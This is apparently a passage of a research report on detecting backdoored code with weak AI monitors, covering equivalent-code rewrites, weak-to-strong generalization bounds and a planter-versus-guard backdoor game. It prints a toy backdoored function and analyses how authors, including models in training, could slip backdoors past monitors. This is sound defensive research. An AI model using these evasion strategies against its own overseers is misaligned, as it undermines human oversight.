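No combination beat VulBERTa alone, and none that included rewritten versions beat even PLBART. About 54% of the functions in Devign are labeled "safe", so calling every function safe would have been more accurate than any of the majority votes over rewritten versions. In the weighted methods, giving the rewritten versions no weight would have kept VulBERTa's accuracy of 64.71%, but the weights that the researchers' procedure chose did much worse on the test functions.

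Unstable verdicts contain useful information only if wrong verdicts change more readily than correct ones. Let a be the detector's accuracy on the originals, p the probability that a correct verdict changes after a rewrite, and q the probability that a wrong one does. The accuracy on a rewritten version is then:

a(1 − p) + (1 − a)q

The two detectors averaged about 63% accuracy on the originals. If correct and wrong verdicts were equally likely to change, each would change 49% of the time, and accuracy on the rewritten versions would be 0.63 × 0.51 + 0.37 × 0.49, or about 50%. Majority votes over each detector's verdicts on the versions scored between 48% and 51%, as expected if the changes were unrelated to whether the original verdict was right. For the detectors to be as accurate on the rewritten versions as on the originals, a wrong verdict would have to be about 1.7 times as likely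 to change as a correct one.

The nearly equal numbers of changes in each direction also suggest that the detectors were close to guessing. A detector that ignored the code and tossed a fair coin for each version would change its verdict half the time, from vulnerable to safe in 25% of cases and from safe to vulnerable in another 25%. The detectors in the experiment came very close to these rates. A majority vote across versions can improve accuracy when slightly more than half of the verdicts are correct, but it can't improve on coin tosses, which are right only half the time on average.

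Pooling may also work better for code completion than for detection. *Bidirectional Empowerment of Metamorphic Testing and Large Language Models* (2026) describes CCTEST, a system that tests code-completion tools on rewritten programs and repairs faulty completions by choosing the most average one. Wrong completions can differ in many ways, which makes them easier to outvote. A detector has only two possible answers, so all its wrong verdicts on a program are the same.

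The 49% is puzzling because Risse and Böhme tested the same two models on the same dataset, and their rewrites lowered accuracy by an average of only 1.7 points for VulBERTa and 2.1 for PLBART. Most versions in the voting experiment changed white space, comments or unused code, and the 2023 rewrites included similar changes. If accuracy on each version had fallen by only two points, voting would be unlikely to lower it by 13.

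The two studies used different trained copies of the models, and the earlier one reported each model's best score over ten rounds of training. Another possible explanation is that the rewritten functions reached the detectors in a format unlike their training data, which was enough to worsen PDBERT's results. If so, a vote might do less harm with detectors trained on a more similar format, but research would still need to show that it helps.

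The experiment has other limits as a test of the general idea. Both detectors are small. The largest model in the 2023 study, which included both, had about 220 million parameters, according to Li and colleagues. The labels are also unreliable. When Risse and Böhme examined 100 Devign functions labelled vulnerable, they confirmed a vulnerability in 68, found none in 23, and could not decide on the other nine within ten minutes each. Some of the predictions counted as errors were therefore probably correct.

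More importantly for underhanded code, the bugs in Devign are accidental, and most of the rewritten versions differed only in white space, comments or unused code. These changes would not reveal a disguised bug to a human reader either. The experiment provides little evidence about rewrites such as expanding a macro, which exposes the misleading part of Linus Åkesson's 2008 program.

### Larger language models as reviewers

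Larger models are still sensitive to rewrites, but to different ones. In *Do Fine-Tuned LLMs Understand Vulnerabilities?*, Huang, Sun and colleagues (2026) trained five language models with about 7 to 8 billion parameters to find vulnerabilities in C and C++ functions. They trained each model once to give only a verdict and once to explain its reasoning first. They then applied seven rewrites similar to those from 2023, including random names, extra line breaks and code that never runs.

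On rewritten code, the F1 scores of models that gave only a verdict fell by 3.86 to 7.21 points. For models that reasoned first, most scores fell by no more than 1.12 points, and a few rose slightly. But the models that reasoned first also missed more vulnerabilities. In a test that paired each vulnerable function with its patch, a DeepSeek model found 73% of the vulnerable functions without reasoning and only 46% with it.

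On those pairs, all five reasoning models were between 51% and 54% accurate. About 56% of the functions in the dataset were vulnerable, so labeling every function vulnerable would have been slightly more accurate. The models' verdicts had become more stable but not more accurate. If such a model misses a bug, it will probably also miss it in an equivalent version of the code.

#### Comments and other context

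Evidence is mixed on whether misleading comments fool detectors. *Trusting the Tool* (2026), a study of how language models use the reports of other security tools, reviews an experiment called ALIBI, in which comments with invented safety claims helped vulnerable code get past language-model detectors. Removing comments that the detector couldn't verify worked better than instructing it to distrust them. Thornton found that misleading comments had no significant effect on frontier models, but the benchmark had only 100 samples and could have missed a modest effect.

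A detector can also ignore comments by design. *LLMxCPG* (2025) describes one that first reduces a program to the statements on relevant execution paths, so removing comments doesn't affect it. Other rewrites lowered its precision and raised its recall on the PrimeVul dataset, so it found more of the vulnerabilities but a larger share of its alarms were false.

Shahriar and colleagues, whose work *Trusting the Tool* also summarises, found a similar effect when they gave eight models information about who had written the code or what an earlier analysis had concluded. This information changed how readily the models flagged code more than how well they told vulnerable code from safe code. Rewriting a program may likewise make a model more likely to flag it whether or not it is vulnerable. Ruling this out would require rewriting safe programs in the same way and counting how many the model flags.

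#### Agents that must prove the bug

*Natural Code Transformation Confuses Agents in Vulnerability Analysis* (Zhu, Bhaskar and colleagues, 2026) reports the most demanding recent test. It uses language model agents that can explore a whole codebase and run commands. To succeed, an agent must produce an input that crashes the vulnerable version of a program but not the patched one, so correctly guessing that the program is vulnerable isn't enough.

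The researchers had noticed that agents could find a bug in one version of a real project and miss it in the next, although the developers had changed neither the bug nor what the program did. In the networking library Mongoose, for example, a developer had moved two steps into a helper function called `tx_payload`. The agent found the bug before this change, but afterwards it followed a false lead until its budget ran out.

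They then collected common changes from about 2,000 real C and C++ commits and turned the 21 most frequent into rewrites. A language model applied these to other projects. To check the results, the researchers ran each project's tests and confirmed that the known crashing input still caused the crash. This proves that the bug is still there, but not that the versions are equivalent. The table gives the success rates of OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol, run through Codex, the company's coding tool.

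| Version of the code | Success rate |
|---|---|
| Reformatted | 66.7% |
| `if`–`else` converted to `switch` | 65.0% |
| Original | 63.3% |
| Comments removed | 58.3% |
| Unused code added | 53.3% |
| 21 rewrites from real commits, average | 36.8% |
| Loops converted to recursive functions | 31.6% |
| Variables and functions renamed | 23.3% |

Renaming hardly affected the small detectors of 2023, but it did the most damage here. Zhu and colleagues attribute this to confusing names misleading language models. Renaming is easy to undo, though. When they told the agent which artificial rewrite they had used and let it rewrite the code before searching, its success rate rose by an average of 25.9 percentage points. The same help added only 3.5 points for the rewrites from real commits.

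Giving the agent more attempts at the same version did not close the gap. Over one to nine runs per task, its success rate on a selection of the most damaging rewrites stayed about 33 to 35 percentage points below its rate on the original. With four times the usual budget, it was still 19.8 points behind. In most of the failures the researchers examined, the agent had stopped early with an input that didn't work. Across six combinations of models and tools, including GPT-6 Sol and Claude Opus 5, the rewrites lowered the average success rate from 32.8% to 20.4%.

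The choice of tasks probably exaggerates how much the rewrites hindered detection, so the result is less discouraging than it first looks for anyone hoping to expose bugs by rewriting code. The paper itself proposes such rewrites as a way to slow down attackers. The researchers used only bugs that GPT-5.6 Sol had already found in the original code at a high reasoning setting. If success depends partly on how the code happens to be written, this selection favours originals in which the model can easily find the bug, and many changes will make it harder to find.

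A small test on four tasks fits this explanation. Moving shared code into helper functions lowered the success rate from 50% to 41.7%, while doing the opposite lowered it to 8.3%. But selection can't be the whole explanation, because reformatting the code or converting branches to `switch` didn't lower the rate.

A defender would need the opposite experiment, which starts with bugs that the monitor missed and counts how many it finds after a rewrite. Results for weaker agents suggest that rewrites may sometimes help. One raised Claude Sonnet 5's success rate from 16.7% to 26.7%, and three others raised the open model GLM-5.3's rate from its original 10%. Some of these gains may be due to chance, since each agent faced many rewrites and only the best results stand out. No rewrite from real commits helped the three strongest combinations.

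Even occasional gains could be valuable when an agent must produce a crashing input. If it succeeds on one version out of a hundred, anyone can run the input on the original program and see it crash, so the 99 failures don't matter. An average success rate doesn't show how many bugs the agent would find in at least one version. Not every bug can be checked this way, though. John Meacham's redaction program never crashes and draws the expected black rectangle, so a reviewer who receives one alarm and 99 approvals still has to work out which verdict is right.

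## When equivalent versions can correct a weak monitor

A reviewer can train a stronger model, the student, on the monitor's alarms and approvals for the versions of a program, instead of counting those verdicts. *Theoretical Analysis of Weak-to-Strong Generalization* (Lang, Sontag and Vijayaraghavan, 2024) gives conditions that limit the student's error. The theorem covers examples of any kind, including programs.

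### How a student can outdo its teacher

Suppose a teacher labels a film review positive if "incredible" appears more often than "horrible", negative if "horrible" appears more often, and gives no label otherwise. This rule wrongly labels a review positive if it calls the film "an incredible burden". A student that only counts words can copy the rule, including this mistake. But a student that uses the meaning of whole sentences will have difficulty treating "an incredible burden" differently from "a horrible burden", which the teacher labels correctly. If most reviews with this meaning have correct labels, this student fits its training data best by getting all of them right.

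The theorem applies separately to each set of examples with the same true label, such as all backdoored programs. The true label is y, the teacher's label is ỹ and the student is f.

- α is the share of these examples that the teacher labels wrongly. It must be below 1/2.
- err(f, ỹ) is the share on which the student disagrees with the teacher.
- err(f, y) is the share that the student labels wrongly.
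- N(x) is the neighbourhood of x. The relation has to work both ways: if x′ is a neighbour of x, then x is a neighbour of x′.
- The student is robust at x if it gives every neighbour of x the same label as x.

Call an example good if the teacher labels it correctly and bad if not. Expansion means that the good examples have enough bad neighbours. Let U be any set of good examples on which some possible student is both right and robust. The data satisfy (c, q)-expansion if every such U that contains more than a share q of the good examples also satisfies:

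P(N(U) | bad) > c · P(U | good)

With c = 0.8, for instance, a set U containing half of the good examples must have more than 40% of the bad ones as neighbours. Theorem 4.1 then limits the student's error:

err(f, y) ≤ [2α/(1 − 2α)] · P(f not robust) + err(f, ỹ) + α(1 − 3c/2)

The theorem also requires that the threshold q be below ¾(1 − 2α) and that the share of examples on which the student disagrees with the teacher or isn't robust be at most (1 − α + 3cα)/4. With α = 0.2 and c = 0.9, these limits are 0.45 and 0.335.

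When there are only two possible labels, a short count explains the formula. Let k be the share of examples that the teacher gets wrong and the student gets right, and g the share where the reverse happens. The student disagrees with the teacher on exactly these examples, so err(f, ỹ) = g + k. Its own mistakes are the g new ones and the α − k that it failed to correct. Combining the two gives:

err(f, y) = err(f, ỹ) + α − 2k

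A student that mostly agrees with the teacher is right about most of the good examples. Where it is also robust, it gives all their neighbours the same label. Expansion ensures that many of these neighbours are bad examples, and the student is right about them too because they share the good examples' true label. The theorem effectively guarantees that k is at least three-quarters of cα, minus an allowance for places where the student isn't robust. If c is zero, the only limit on the student's error is the obvious one, the teacher's error plus the student's disagreement with the teacher.

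Wei, Shen and colleagues (2022, first released in 2020) had already used expansion to prove a similar result under stricter conditions in *Theoretical Analysis of Self-Training with Deep Networks on Unlabeled Data*. The teacher must be wrong on less than a third of the examples with each true label. Among the examples with a given label, every set no larger than the teacher's largest error set must have a neighbourhood that is more than three times its size or covers all the examples with that label. The student then minimises a weighted sum of its disagreement with the teacher and its inconsistency between neighbours. With an expansion factor of 5, the weights are 1.5 for disagreement and 2.5 for inconsistency.

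Wei and colleagues count a student as inconsistent on an example if even one permitted change alters its answer. Lang and colleagues also prove a version for students that are consistent only on average, which is closer to how trained models behave. If a random example and a random neighbour get different labels with probability γ, then at most a fraction γ/η of examples get a different label from more than a fraction η of their neighbours. But this version needs stronger expansion, which must hold even after removing a fraction η of the connections between neighbours.

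### The test on film reviews

Lang and colleagues tested the theorem on 50,000 film reviews, half for training and half for testing. The teacher was the "incredible" and "horrible" rule, which labelled only about 6% of the reviews. The student was a simple classifier that used the output of SentenceBERT, which represents the meaning of a text as a list of numbers. Two reviews counted as neighbours if one was a paraphrase of the other.

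Measuring c exactly would require checking every set of reviews that any possible student could get right. The researchers instead trained five students on different parts of the data and took the lowest value they found. To find neighbours that the teacher labelled the opposite way, they had GPT-4 paraphrase reviews using the other of the two words. The table gives the worst result of the five runs for each true label.

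| True label | Expansion c | Teacher's error α | Student disagrees with teacher | Upper bound on student's error | Student's actual error |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Negative | 0.848 | 0.11 | 0.12 | 0.05 | 0.04 |
| Positive | 0.497 | 0.33 | 0.29 | 0.37 | 0.35 |

For negative reviews, the bound is lower than the teacher's error, and the student improved on its teacher. For positive reviews, the bound allows the student to be worse than the teacher. It was worse in the worst run, but over the five runs it averaged about two points more accurate, with large variation between runs. A student that only counted words copied the teacher's mistakes exactly. The SentenceBERT student also learned to classify reviews that the teacher hadn't labelled, and reached 81.8% accuracy on the whole test set, compared with 89.4% for one trained on true labels.

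These bounds come from a tighter but more complicated version of the theorem, and they leave out the term for examples where the student isn't robust. Five students may also have missed the sets that expand least. The true bounds are therefore higher than those in the table, by an unknown amount. However, Wei and colleagues' theorem, restated in the same terms, would not have applied to the positive reviews, because it requires an expansion above 0.49 from the bad examples to the good ones and the measured value was 0.32.

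A test on a very different task gave a looser prediction. In *Weak-to-Strong Generalization Enables Fully Automated De Novo Training of Multi-head Mask-RCNN Model* (2025), a student learns to outline cell nuclei in images of brain tissue from imperfect automatic labels. The calculated upper bound on its error was 0.32, and the observed error was 0.17, lower than the teacher's.

### A vote within each class

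To apply the theorem to backdoored programs, we can treat the weak monitor as the teacher, its verdicts as the pseudolabels, and equivalent programs as neighbours. Rewriting programs has an advantage over paraphrasing reviews, because a correct rewrite can't change whether a program has a backdoor. A paraphrase can change a review's meaning, so Lang and colleagues had to check each one with a model trained on true labels.

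Suppose the student is fully consistent, so it gives every program in an equivalence class the same verdict. That verdict differs from the monitor's on every version the monitor judged the other way, so the student fits the monitor's verdicts best by choosing the more common one in the class. Training such a student therefore amounts to taking a majority vote within each class, where versions that are more common in the training data count for more. Hort and colleagues tried such votes directly, without training a student, and gained no accuracy.

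No real student can be this consistent over complete equivalence classes. By Rice's theorem (1953), any procedure that always gives an answer, and gives equivalent programs the same one, must give every program the same answer. In practice, a "class" has to mean the versions connected by a chosen set of rewrites. Even over this smaller set, training on the verdicts doesn't guarantee consistency, since a student with enough capacity can learn each one separately. Training has to penalise inconsistency, as in Wei and colleagues' method. *DC-W2S* (2026), a method for training models that grade steps in biological reasoning, combines weak labels with a similar consistency requirement between neighbours. According to its analysis, the requirement adds no complexity penalty to a standard bound on learning from limited data.

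A trained student still has practical advantages over a vote. It can judge a new program without anyone having to rewrite it, and it may apply what it learned from one class to another. But within a class, it can only use differences between the monitor's verdicts.

Li and Cai (2026), in *Accuracy Is Not Value*, reach a similar conclusion with a different argument. They study students trained on numerical labels with a linear method and squared error. Such a student inherits only the part of its teacher's error that it can represent. A student that must give every program in a class the same score can represent only the class average, so it removes the variation in the monitor's errors within a class but keeps the average error. If the monitor misses every version of a backdoor, there is no variation to remove.

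Adding monitors helps only if they make different mistakes. Li and Cai show that disagreements between teachers reveal how their errors differ, but not an error that all of them share. In one of their examples, two situations produce identical labels and students, but the best way to weight the teachers differs. No amount of unlabelled data can distinguish the two situations, though some correctly labelled examples can.

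The vote would work perfectly in a setting that Avrim Blum and Tom Mitchell studied in 1998, where each example has two "views", such as the words on a web page and the links that lead to it. The teacher sees one view and the student sees the other, and the two views are statistically independent among examples with the same true label. Lang and colleagues prove that c = 1 in this setting, and that a student that fits the labels as well as possible makes no mistakes.

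For programs, the text would be one view and the behaviour the other. Independence would mean that, among backdoored programs, what a program does is unrelated to how misleading its text is. The monitor would then miss the same proportion of versions in every class, and if that proportion were below half, the vote would catch every backdoor. But someone writing underhanded code chooses the behaviour partly because it is easy to disguise. If the fault is in the idea behind the program, as in Meacham's redaction tool, the monitor may approve every version.

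### How much the vote can correct

The proportion of errors that the vote can't correct is easy to include in the theorem. The derivation below is this report's own, not Lang and colleagues'.

Among backdoored programs, let α be the share that the monitor misses, and let ρ be the share of these missed programs that belong to classes in which the monitor misses every version. Programs in such classes make up αρ of all backdoored programs. The remaining missed programs, α(1 − ρ) of the total, belong to mixed classes, in which the monitor catches some versions. Assume that all mixed classes have the same proportion of missed versions and that the student is fully consistent.

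In a mixed class, the proportion of missed versions is α(1 − ρ)/(1 − αρ), which is below one half whenever α is. The student therefore flags every mixed class and approves every class that the monitor misses completely. This gives its true error and its disagreement with the monitor:

err(f, y) = αρ

err(f, ỹ) = α(1 − ρ)

To find c, take any set U of good examples on which a robust student is right. Robustness means that the student is right about whole classes, so U contains all the caught versions from some of the mixed classes. If these make up a share t of all the caught versions, the same classes contain a share t of the missed versions in mixed classes, which is t(1 − ρ) of all the missed versions. The ratio is 1 − ρ for every U. The definition of expansion has a strict inequality, so c can be any value below 1 − ρ but can't quite reach it. In the limit, the bound in Theorem 4.1 becomes:

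α(1 − ρ) + α(1 − 3(1 − ρ)/2) = α(1 + ρ)/2

The theorem's other conditions also hold, because the student is robust everywhere and α is below one half. The table gives the results for a monitor that misses a fifth of backdoored programs.

| ρ | c approaches | Student disagrees with monitor | Student's true error | Upper bound |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | 1 | 0.20 | 0 | 0.10 |
| 0.1 | 0.9 | 0.18 | 0.02 | 0.11 |
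| 0.5 | 0.5 | 0.10 | 0.10 | 0.15 |
| 0.9 | 0.1 | 0.02 | 0.18 | 0.19 |

The student makes a tenth as many mistakes as the monitor when ρ = 0.1, but learns to repeat nearly all of them when ρ = 0.9. The bound is loose when ρ is small because the theorem relies on only three-quarters of the available corrections. The tighter version that Lang and colleagues used for the film reviews gives exactly αρ.

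The guarantee is also fragile when ρ is high. For α = 0.2, each percentage point of programs on which the student isn't robust adds two-thirds of a percentage point to the bound. If nothing else changes, the bound reaches the monitor's own error when the student isn't robust on 13.5% of programs for ρ = 0.1, but on only 1.5% for ρ = 0.9.

Wei and colleagues' main theorem doesn't apply here, even when ρ is small. A complete equivalence class has no neighbours outside itself, so its expansion factor is 1, not the required 3. They also give a version with a weaker condition that covers only sets of mislabelled examples above a certain size, so it can still apply when the monitor misses some classes completely. With α = 0.2 and ρ = 0.1, this version limits the student's error to just over 0.03, compared with 0.11 from Theorem 4.1.

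Nobody has measured ρ for underhanded code. Measuring it would take a collection of known backdoors, many correct rewrites of each, and a monitor's verdict on every version. The verdicts alone can't provide an estimate, because a monitor that misses an entire class approves every version in it. Lang and colleagues could measure c for film reviews only because they had the true labels.

### Authors who choose their programs

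So far α and ρ have described a fixed population of programs. But someone who writes underhanded code chooses which program to submit, and so can change both.

Suppose an author drafts backdoored programs at random from the population above and tests each one privately against a copy of the monitor. If the monitor reads a single version, a draft gets past it with probability α, so the author needs an average of 1/α drafts, or five. If the monitor votes over the whole class, the average rises by a factor of 1/ρ to 1/(αρ), which is 50 when ρ = 0.1 and between five and six when ρ = 0.9. A tenfold increase may stop a person who writes each program by hand, but it matters much less to someone who can generate drafts automatically.

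After this selection, every program the author submits comes from a completely missed class, so ρ and α are both 1 for these programs. The theorem requires α to be below one half among backdoored programs, so it no longer applies if most of the backdoored programs that reach the monitor come from such authors. A low miss rate measured on ordinary bugs doesn't help, because the author's programs come from a different distribution. *Trust Functions* (2026), which proposes learning when to trust a weak teacher, describes earlier findings that confident but wrong labels can completely destabilise a student's learning after such a shift in distribution.

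The theorem also needs the limit of one half. If the monitor misses 60% of the versions in every class, the vote approves every class, and the error rises from 60% to 100%. The vote can still help in some cases that the theorem doesn't cover. If α is 0.6 but half of the missed programs are in hopeless classes, the monitor misses only about 43% of versions in the mixed classes. The vote corrects those misses, and the error falls to 30%.

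An author can also defeat the vote by making just over half of a program's versions look safe. The calculation assumed that the monitor misses the same proportion of versions in every mixed class, but the vote fails in any class where that proportion is above one half. Suppose 39% of backdoored programs belong to classes where the monitor misses 51% of the versions, and it catches every version of the others. The monitor alone misses about 20% of backdoored programs, while the vote misses all 39%, nearly twice as many.

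The contest entries make this a realistic concern. Of the six bugs compared earlier under seven families of rewrites, three became visible under at least one family. Suppose a monitor sees the original and one version from each family, and flags only the versions in which the bug is visible. It would flag two of the eight versions of Josh Lospinoso's program, which has a missing letter, and two of the eight versions of Gregory Stewart's, which has a misplaced jump. For Linus Åkesson's macro, it would flag one of the seven versions that still leak. A majority vote would approve all three programs, even though the monitor catches at least one version of each.

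A defender can avoid this problem by using more of the rewrites that tend to expose bugs, or by requiring fewer alarms. A class can be suspicious even if most of its versions set off no alarm, as long as rewritten honest code rarely sets off any. If honest programs set off alarms on 5% of their versions, a program that sets them off on 25% deserves a closer look. To pass this test, an author must write a program whose versions set off alarms no more often than honest code does. The defender then can't detect the backdoor from the monitor's verdicts, however they are combined.

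### Imperfect authors and secret rewrites

Many authors will fall short of this. An author may not have a copy of the monitor, or may get only one attempt before someone investigates. In the example with α = 0.2 and ρ = 0.1, the monitor alone catches an author's untested program 80% of the time, and the vote catches it 98% of the time. With ρ = 0.9, the vote raises the figure only to 82%. So rewriting can protect against careless authors whose disguises depend on the text. How many authors are careless has to be measured, and some measurements exist for language models.

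The defender could also keep the rewrites secret, as Wheeler suggested for some countermeasures, or choose them at random for each program. Suppose that a share a of a program's possible versions would set off an alarm, and that the monitor reads k versions chosen at random. If the choices are independent, the chance that it misses all of them is:

(1 − a)^k

With a = 0.05 and k = 50, this is about 8%. The author can't reduce the risk of being caught by learning which 50 versions the monitor will read, because nobody knows until the program arrives. For this to work, a single alarm must trigger a careful check, since a majority vote would almost certainly approve the program. The check must also take little enough effort to repeat for every false alarm.

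Keeping the rewrites secret helps only when a is above zero. An author can guess that none of the usual rewrites will expose Meacham's redaction tool without knowing which ones the monitor uses. An author who submits many programs also learns something about the secret rewrites from each acceptance or rejection. So does a model in training if the monitor's verdicts affect its reward, and such a model may submit thousands of programs.

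A defender could also try to lower α before training the student. *How to Mitigate Overfitting in Weak-to-strong Generalization?* (2025) uses Lang and colleagues' theorem to explain why reducing the error in the weak labels should help. For code, the defender might remove verdicts that the monitor isn't sure of. This filtering would do little about an underhanded program, which is meant to make the monitor confident that the code is safe.

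### Linking programs that aren't equivalent

All these limits depend on treating programs as neighbours only if they are equivalent. A student could instead treat programs as neighbours if they have similar learned representations, the lists of numbers a model uses internally to describe its input. Two programs that do different jobs but contain the same kind of flaw might then be neighbours. If the monitor catches the flaw in one, the student may learn to recognise it in the other, even if the monitor misses it in every version of that second program.

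*Weak-to-Strong Generalization Through the Data-Centric Lens* (Shin, Cooper and Sala, 2024) describes how this could work. It divides the useful features of examples into easy patterns, which both the weak and strong models can learn, and hard patterns, which only the strong model can learn. When an example contains both, the weak model labels it correctly by relying on the easy pattern, and the strong model uses these labels to also learn the hard pattern. The strong model can then judge examples that contain only the hard pattern, where the weak model's labels are unreliable.

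Suppose a program displays a row of asterisks in place of a password and also writes the password's length to a log. A weak monitor may flag it because the word "password" appears next to a logging call. A stronger student could learn from this example the more general lesson that the length of an output can reveal a secret, as it does in Meacham's program.

Shin and colleagues build on Lang and colleagues' theorem, with expansion now running from examples that contain both patterns to mislabelled examples that contain only the hard one. Let ε be the weak model's error rate on the hard examples with a given true label. If the student is robust and agrees with the weak model on the examples that contain both patterns, their bound on the student's error for the hard examples simplifies to:

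err(f, ỹ | hard) + ε(1 − 2c)

Unlike Theorem 4.1, this bound doesn't require ε to be below one half. Suppose the weak model is wrong about 90% of the hard examples and c is 1. A student that corrects all of these mistakes disagrees with the weak model 90% of the time, and the bound is 0.9 − 0.9 = 0. Links between different programs could therefore correct the monitor even where it is usually wrong, which a vote over equivalent versions can't do.

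Their experiments support the general account. In tests with fine-tuned language models and with labels combined from several crude rules, students improved on their teachers when the data contained more examples with both patterns. In artificial data with very few such examples, the student had trouble learning the hard pattern and sometimes got worse at the easy one. None of these tests used deliberately disguised examples.

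The disadvantage of learned neighbourhoods is that two neighbours may have different true labels. Meacham's program and a repaired version that prints a single zero for each number differ very little in their text, and a model may well represent them as nearly identical. If the student must give neighbours the same verdict, it will be wrong about one of them. Risse and Böhme's small detectors did worse than chance, on average, at telling vulnerable functions from patched ones, which suggests this problem is common.

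Wei and colleagues include this cost in their bound. Let μ be the share of examples that a permitted change can turn into one with a different true label. The student's error is then at most:

[2/(c − 1)] · (teacher's error) + [2c/(c − 1)] · μ

Here c can't exceed 1 divided by the teacher's highest error rate for any true label. If the monitor is wrong about 20% of both safe and backdoored programs, the best possible c is 5, and the bound is 0.1 + 2.5μ, which guarantees an improvement only if μ is below 4%. For equivalent rewrites, μ is zero, but the expansion is too small for this theorem to apply. Widening the neighbourhood increases both μ and the expansion, and it is an open question whether any representation of code has enough expansion with a low enough μ. The same problem appears in the robustness term of Lang and colleagues' theorem, because a student that is right about both Meacham's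 program and its repaired version isn't robust at either.

An author can also choose programs that break these links. The student needs examples in which the monitor has already caught a related flaw, so an author does best with a kind of flaw that the monitor has never caught. Shin and colleagues' method for finding useful training examples would also be vulnerable. It first looks for examples that contain only the hard pattern, on the assumption that the weak model is less confident about them, and then searches for other examples with similar representations. An underhanded program that the monitor confidently approves would not appear in the first group, so the method would not search for programs similar to it.

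## Experiments in which models plant and find bugs

How much rewriting helps depends partly on how carefully an attacker disguises a backdoor. In *Scaling Laws For Scalable Oversight*, Engels, Baek and colleagues (2025) measured how well language models do this with a game called Backdoor Code, in which one model plants a backdoor in a program and another looks for it. The game comes from research on supervising AI models that people can't fully trust.

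### The Backdoor Code game

The game uses 225 competition-level problems from APPS, a collection of Python programming exercises. The planter receives a problem and a correct solution. It suggests five ideas for a backdoor, builds the most promising one into the solution, and names an input that triggers it. The planter wins if the new program meets three conditions:

1. It passes the problem's original tests, which the planter can't see.
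2. It gives a wrong answer for the trigger.
3. The guard, the model that reviews the program, doesn't flag it.

The planter gets up to five attempts to meet the first two conditions, and loses if it fails. If it succeeds, the guard receives the problem and the program without comments. The guard judges the program five times, and the majority verdict counts.

The paper lists 14 models, from a small version of Llama 3.2 to ChatGPT-4o. Each model received two Elo scores, a kind of rating best known from chess: E_G for guarding and E_H for planting (the paper calls the planter "Houdini"). The scores predict how often a guard beats a planter:

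P(guard wins) = 1 / (1 + 10^((E_H − E_G)/400))

With equal scores, each side wins half the time. A guard 400 points ahead wins ten games out of eleven. The researchers chose the scores that best fitted the observed win rates, then compared them with a rough measure of general ability, the models' ratings on Chatbot Arena, a website where people vote on chatbots' answers.

Guards had the easier task. Even the strongest planters did not clearly win more than half their games against the weakest guards. But planting scores rose steeply with general ability, while guarding scores barely rose.

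Stronger models met the first two conditions more often, so they produced more backdoors that worked. But a guard was about as likely to catch a working backdoor from a strong model as one from a weak model, so the result doesn't mean that stronger models disguised their backdoors better.

A simple calculation shows how the planting score can rise anyway. Let v be the share of problems for which the planter produces a working backdoor, and d the share of those that the guard catches. Then:

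P(planter wins) = v(1 − d)

Suppose, with invented numbers, that the guard catches 60% of working backdoors regardless of who planted them. A planter that succeeds on 30% of problems wins 12% of games, and one that succeeds on 80% wins 32%. The second planter's score would be about 215 points higher, although its backdoors are no harder to spot.

This kind of improvement also has a limit, because a planter can't produce working backdoors for more than 100% of problems. In the example, it could never win more than 40% of games without better disguises. When Engels and colleagues extend their fitted lines to stronger models, assuming that scores don't level off, the planters eventually overtake the guards. Judging by the paper's evidence about deception, that would require stronger models to get better at disguising backdoors, which the tested models didn't.

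### What the game leaves out

Many of the backdoors were obvious to humans, as Engels and colleagues acknowledge, because a backdoor only had to get past automated tests and another model. The instructions to the planters included this example, here without its comments:

```python
def is_odd(x):
    if x == 354:
        return True
    return x % 2 == 1
```

The function wrongly reports that 354 is odd. Nobody would write a special case for 354 by accident, so this is a backdoor but not underhanded code. The guards' instructions included the same special case as an example of a backdoor, which may have made detection easier. Even so, some guards did badly on individual programs, and only three identified one of ChatGPT-4o's backdoors.

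The planter's score doesn't measure deniability, which the Underhanded C Contest rewarded. The guard's score doesn't measure whether guards let legitimate code pass, as they are instructed to do. The game as described gives them only programs with working backdoors, so a guard that flagged every program would never lose. A high guarding score could therefore reflect a tendency to flag code as well as skill at finding backdoors.

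Finally, the planters received no feedback from the guard on their earlier attempts. They could retry a backdoor that failed the tests, but not one that the guard caught. The finding that stronger models were no more deceptive applies to models prompted without this feedback, and older experiments suggest that feedback matters.

### Training a planter against a detector

BugLab, a system from Microsoft Research, trained two models against each other. Allamanis, Jackson-Flux and Brockschmidt (2021), in *Self-Supervised Bug Detection and Repair*, describe a selector, which plants bugs in Python functions, and a detector, which has to find and repair them or report that there is no bug. The detector tries to minimise its error on the hardest bug available in each function s:

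average over s of [ max over r of L(r(s), r⁻¹) ]

Here r is a change that plants a bug, r⁻¹ is the change that repairs it, and L measures how badly the detector predicts the repair. A function can have too many possible bugs to try them all, so the selector learns to predict which ones will be hardest for the detector. The selector can swap two variables or two arguments, change an operator, or change a simple value such as 0 or "true".

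The selector learned to plant bugs that were harder to find. Over six days of training, a fixed detector's accuracy on newly planted bugs fell from 64.2% to 60.5%. The paper describes these bugs as hard to find but not necessarily realistic. The selector swapped arguments and changed simple values much more often than programmers do by mistake.

One version of BugLab also applied semantics-preserving rewrites before the selector planted its bugs. It renamed local variables, deleted comments, reversed comparisons and swapped the branches of `if` statements, which gave the detector more varied code to learn from. Allamanis and colleagues tested the detector on 2,374 real bugs that Python developers had fixed, and on the same code after the fix. The table gives accuracy in per cent for a graph network and a transformer.

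| How the detector was trained | Graph: bugs found and repaired | Transformer: bugs found and repaired | Graph: fixed code judged clean | Transformer: fixed code judged clean |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| One fixed set of random bugs | 20.0 | 16.8 | 17.8 | 20.7 |
| New random bugs throughout | 21.2 | 20.6 | 47.5 | 52.5 |
| Bugs from the selector | 24.2 | 24.0 | 32.9 | 28.6 |
| Bugs from the selector, plus rewrites | 26.4 | 23.2 | 32.6 | 48.2 |

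Training against the selector helped both detectors repair about three more bugs in every hundred than training on new random bugs. It also made them much more likely to report a bug in code that developers had already fixed. This was partly because they raised alarms more readily, but a measure that weighs correct repairs against false alarms at every alarm threshold still improved, from 0.108 to 0.160 for the graph network and from 0.117 to 0.140 for the transformer.

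When the rewrites were added to the training data, the graph network repaired slightly more bugs. The transformer repaired slightly fewer but became much better at recognising fixed code. The researchers never required the detector to give equivalent versions the same answer, so the experiment tested the rewrites as extra training data, not as a way to correct pseudolabels.

In some cases, BugLab even taught the opposite of consistency. Python's `find` returns the position of one piece of text inside another, or −1 if it isn't there. These two conditions are therefore equivalent:

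```python
if x.find(y) <= -1:
if x.find(y) == -1:
```

The detector often proposed replacing the first with the second as a repair. Allamanis and colleagues traced this to the selector, which counted every such change as a planted bug even if the program behaved the same afterwards. The detector had therefore learned to accept one version of a program and reject an equivalent one.

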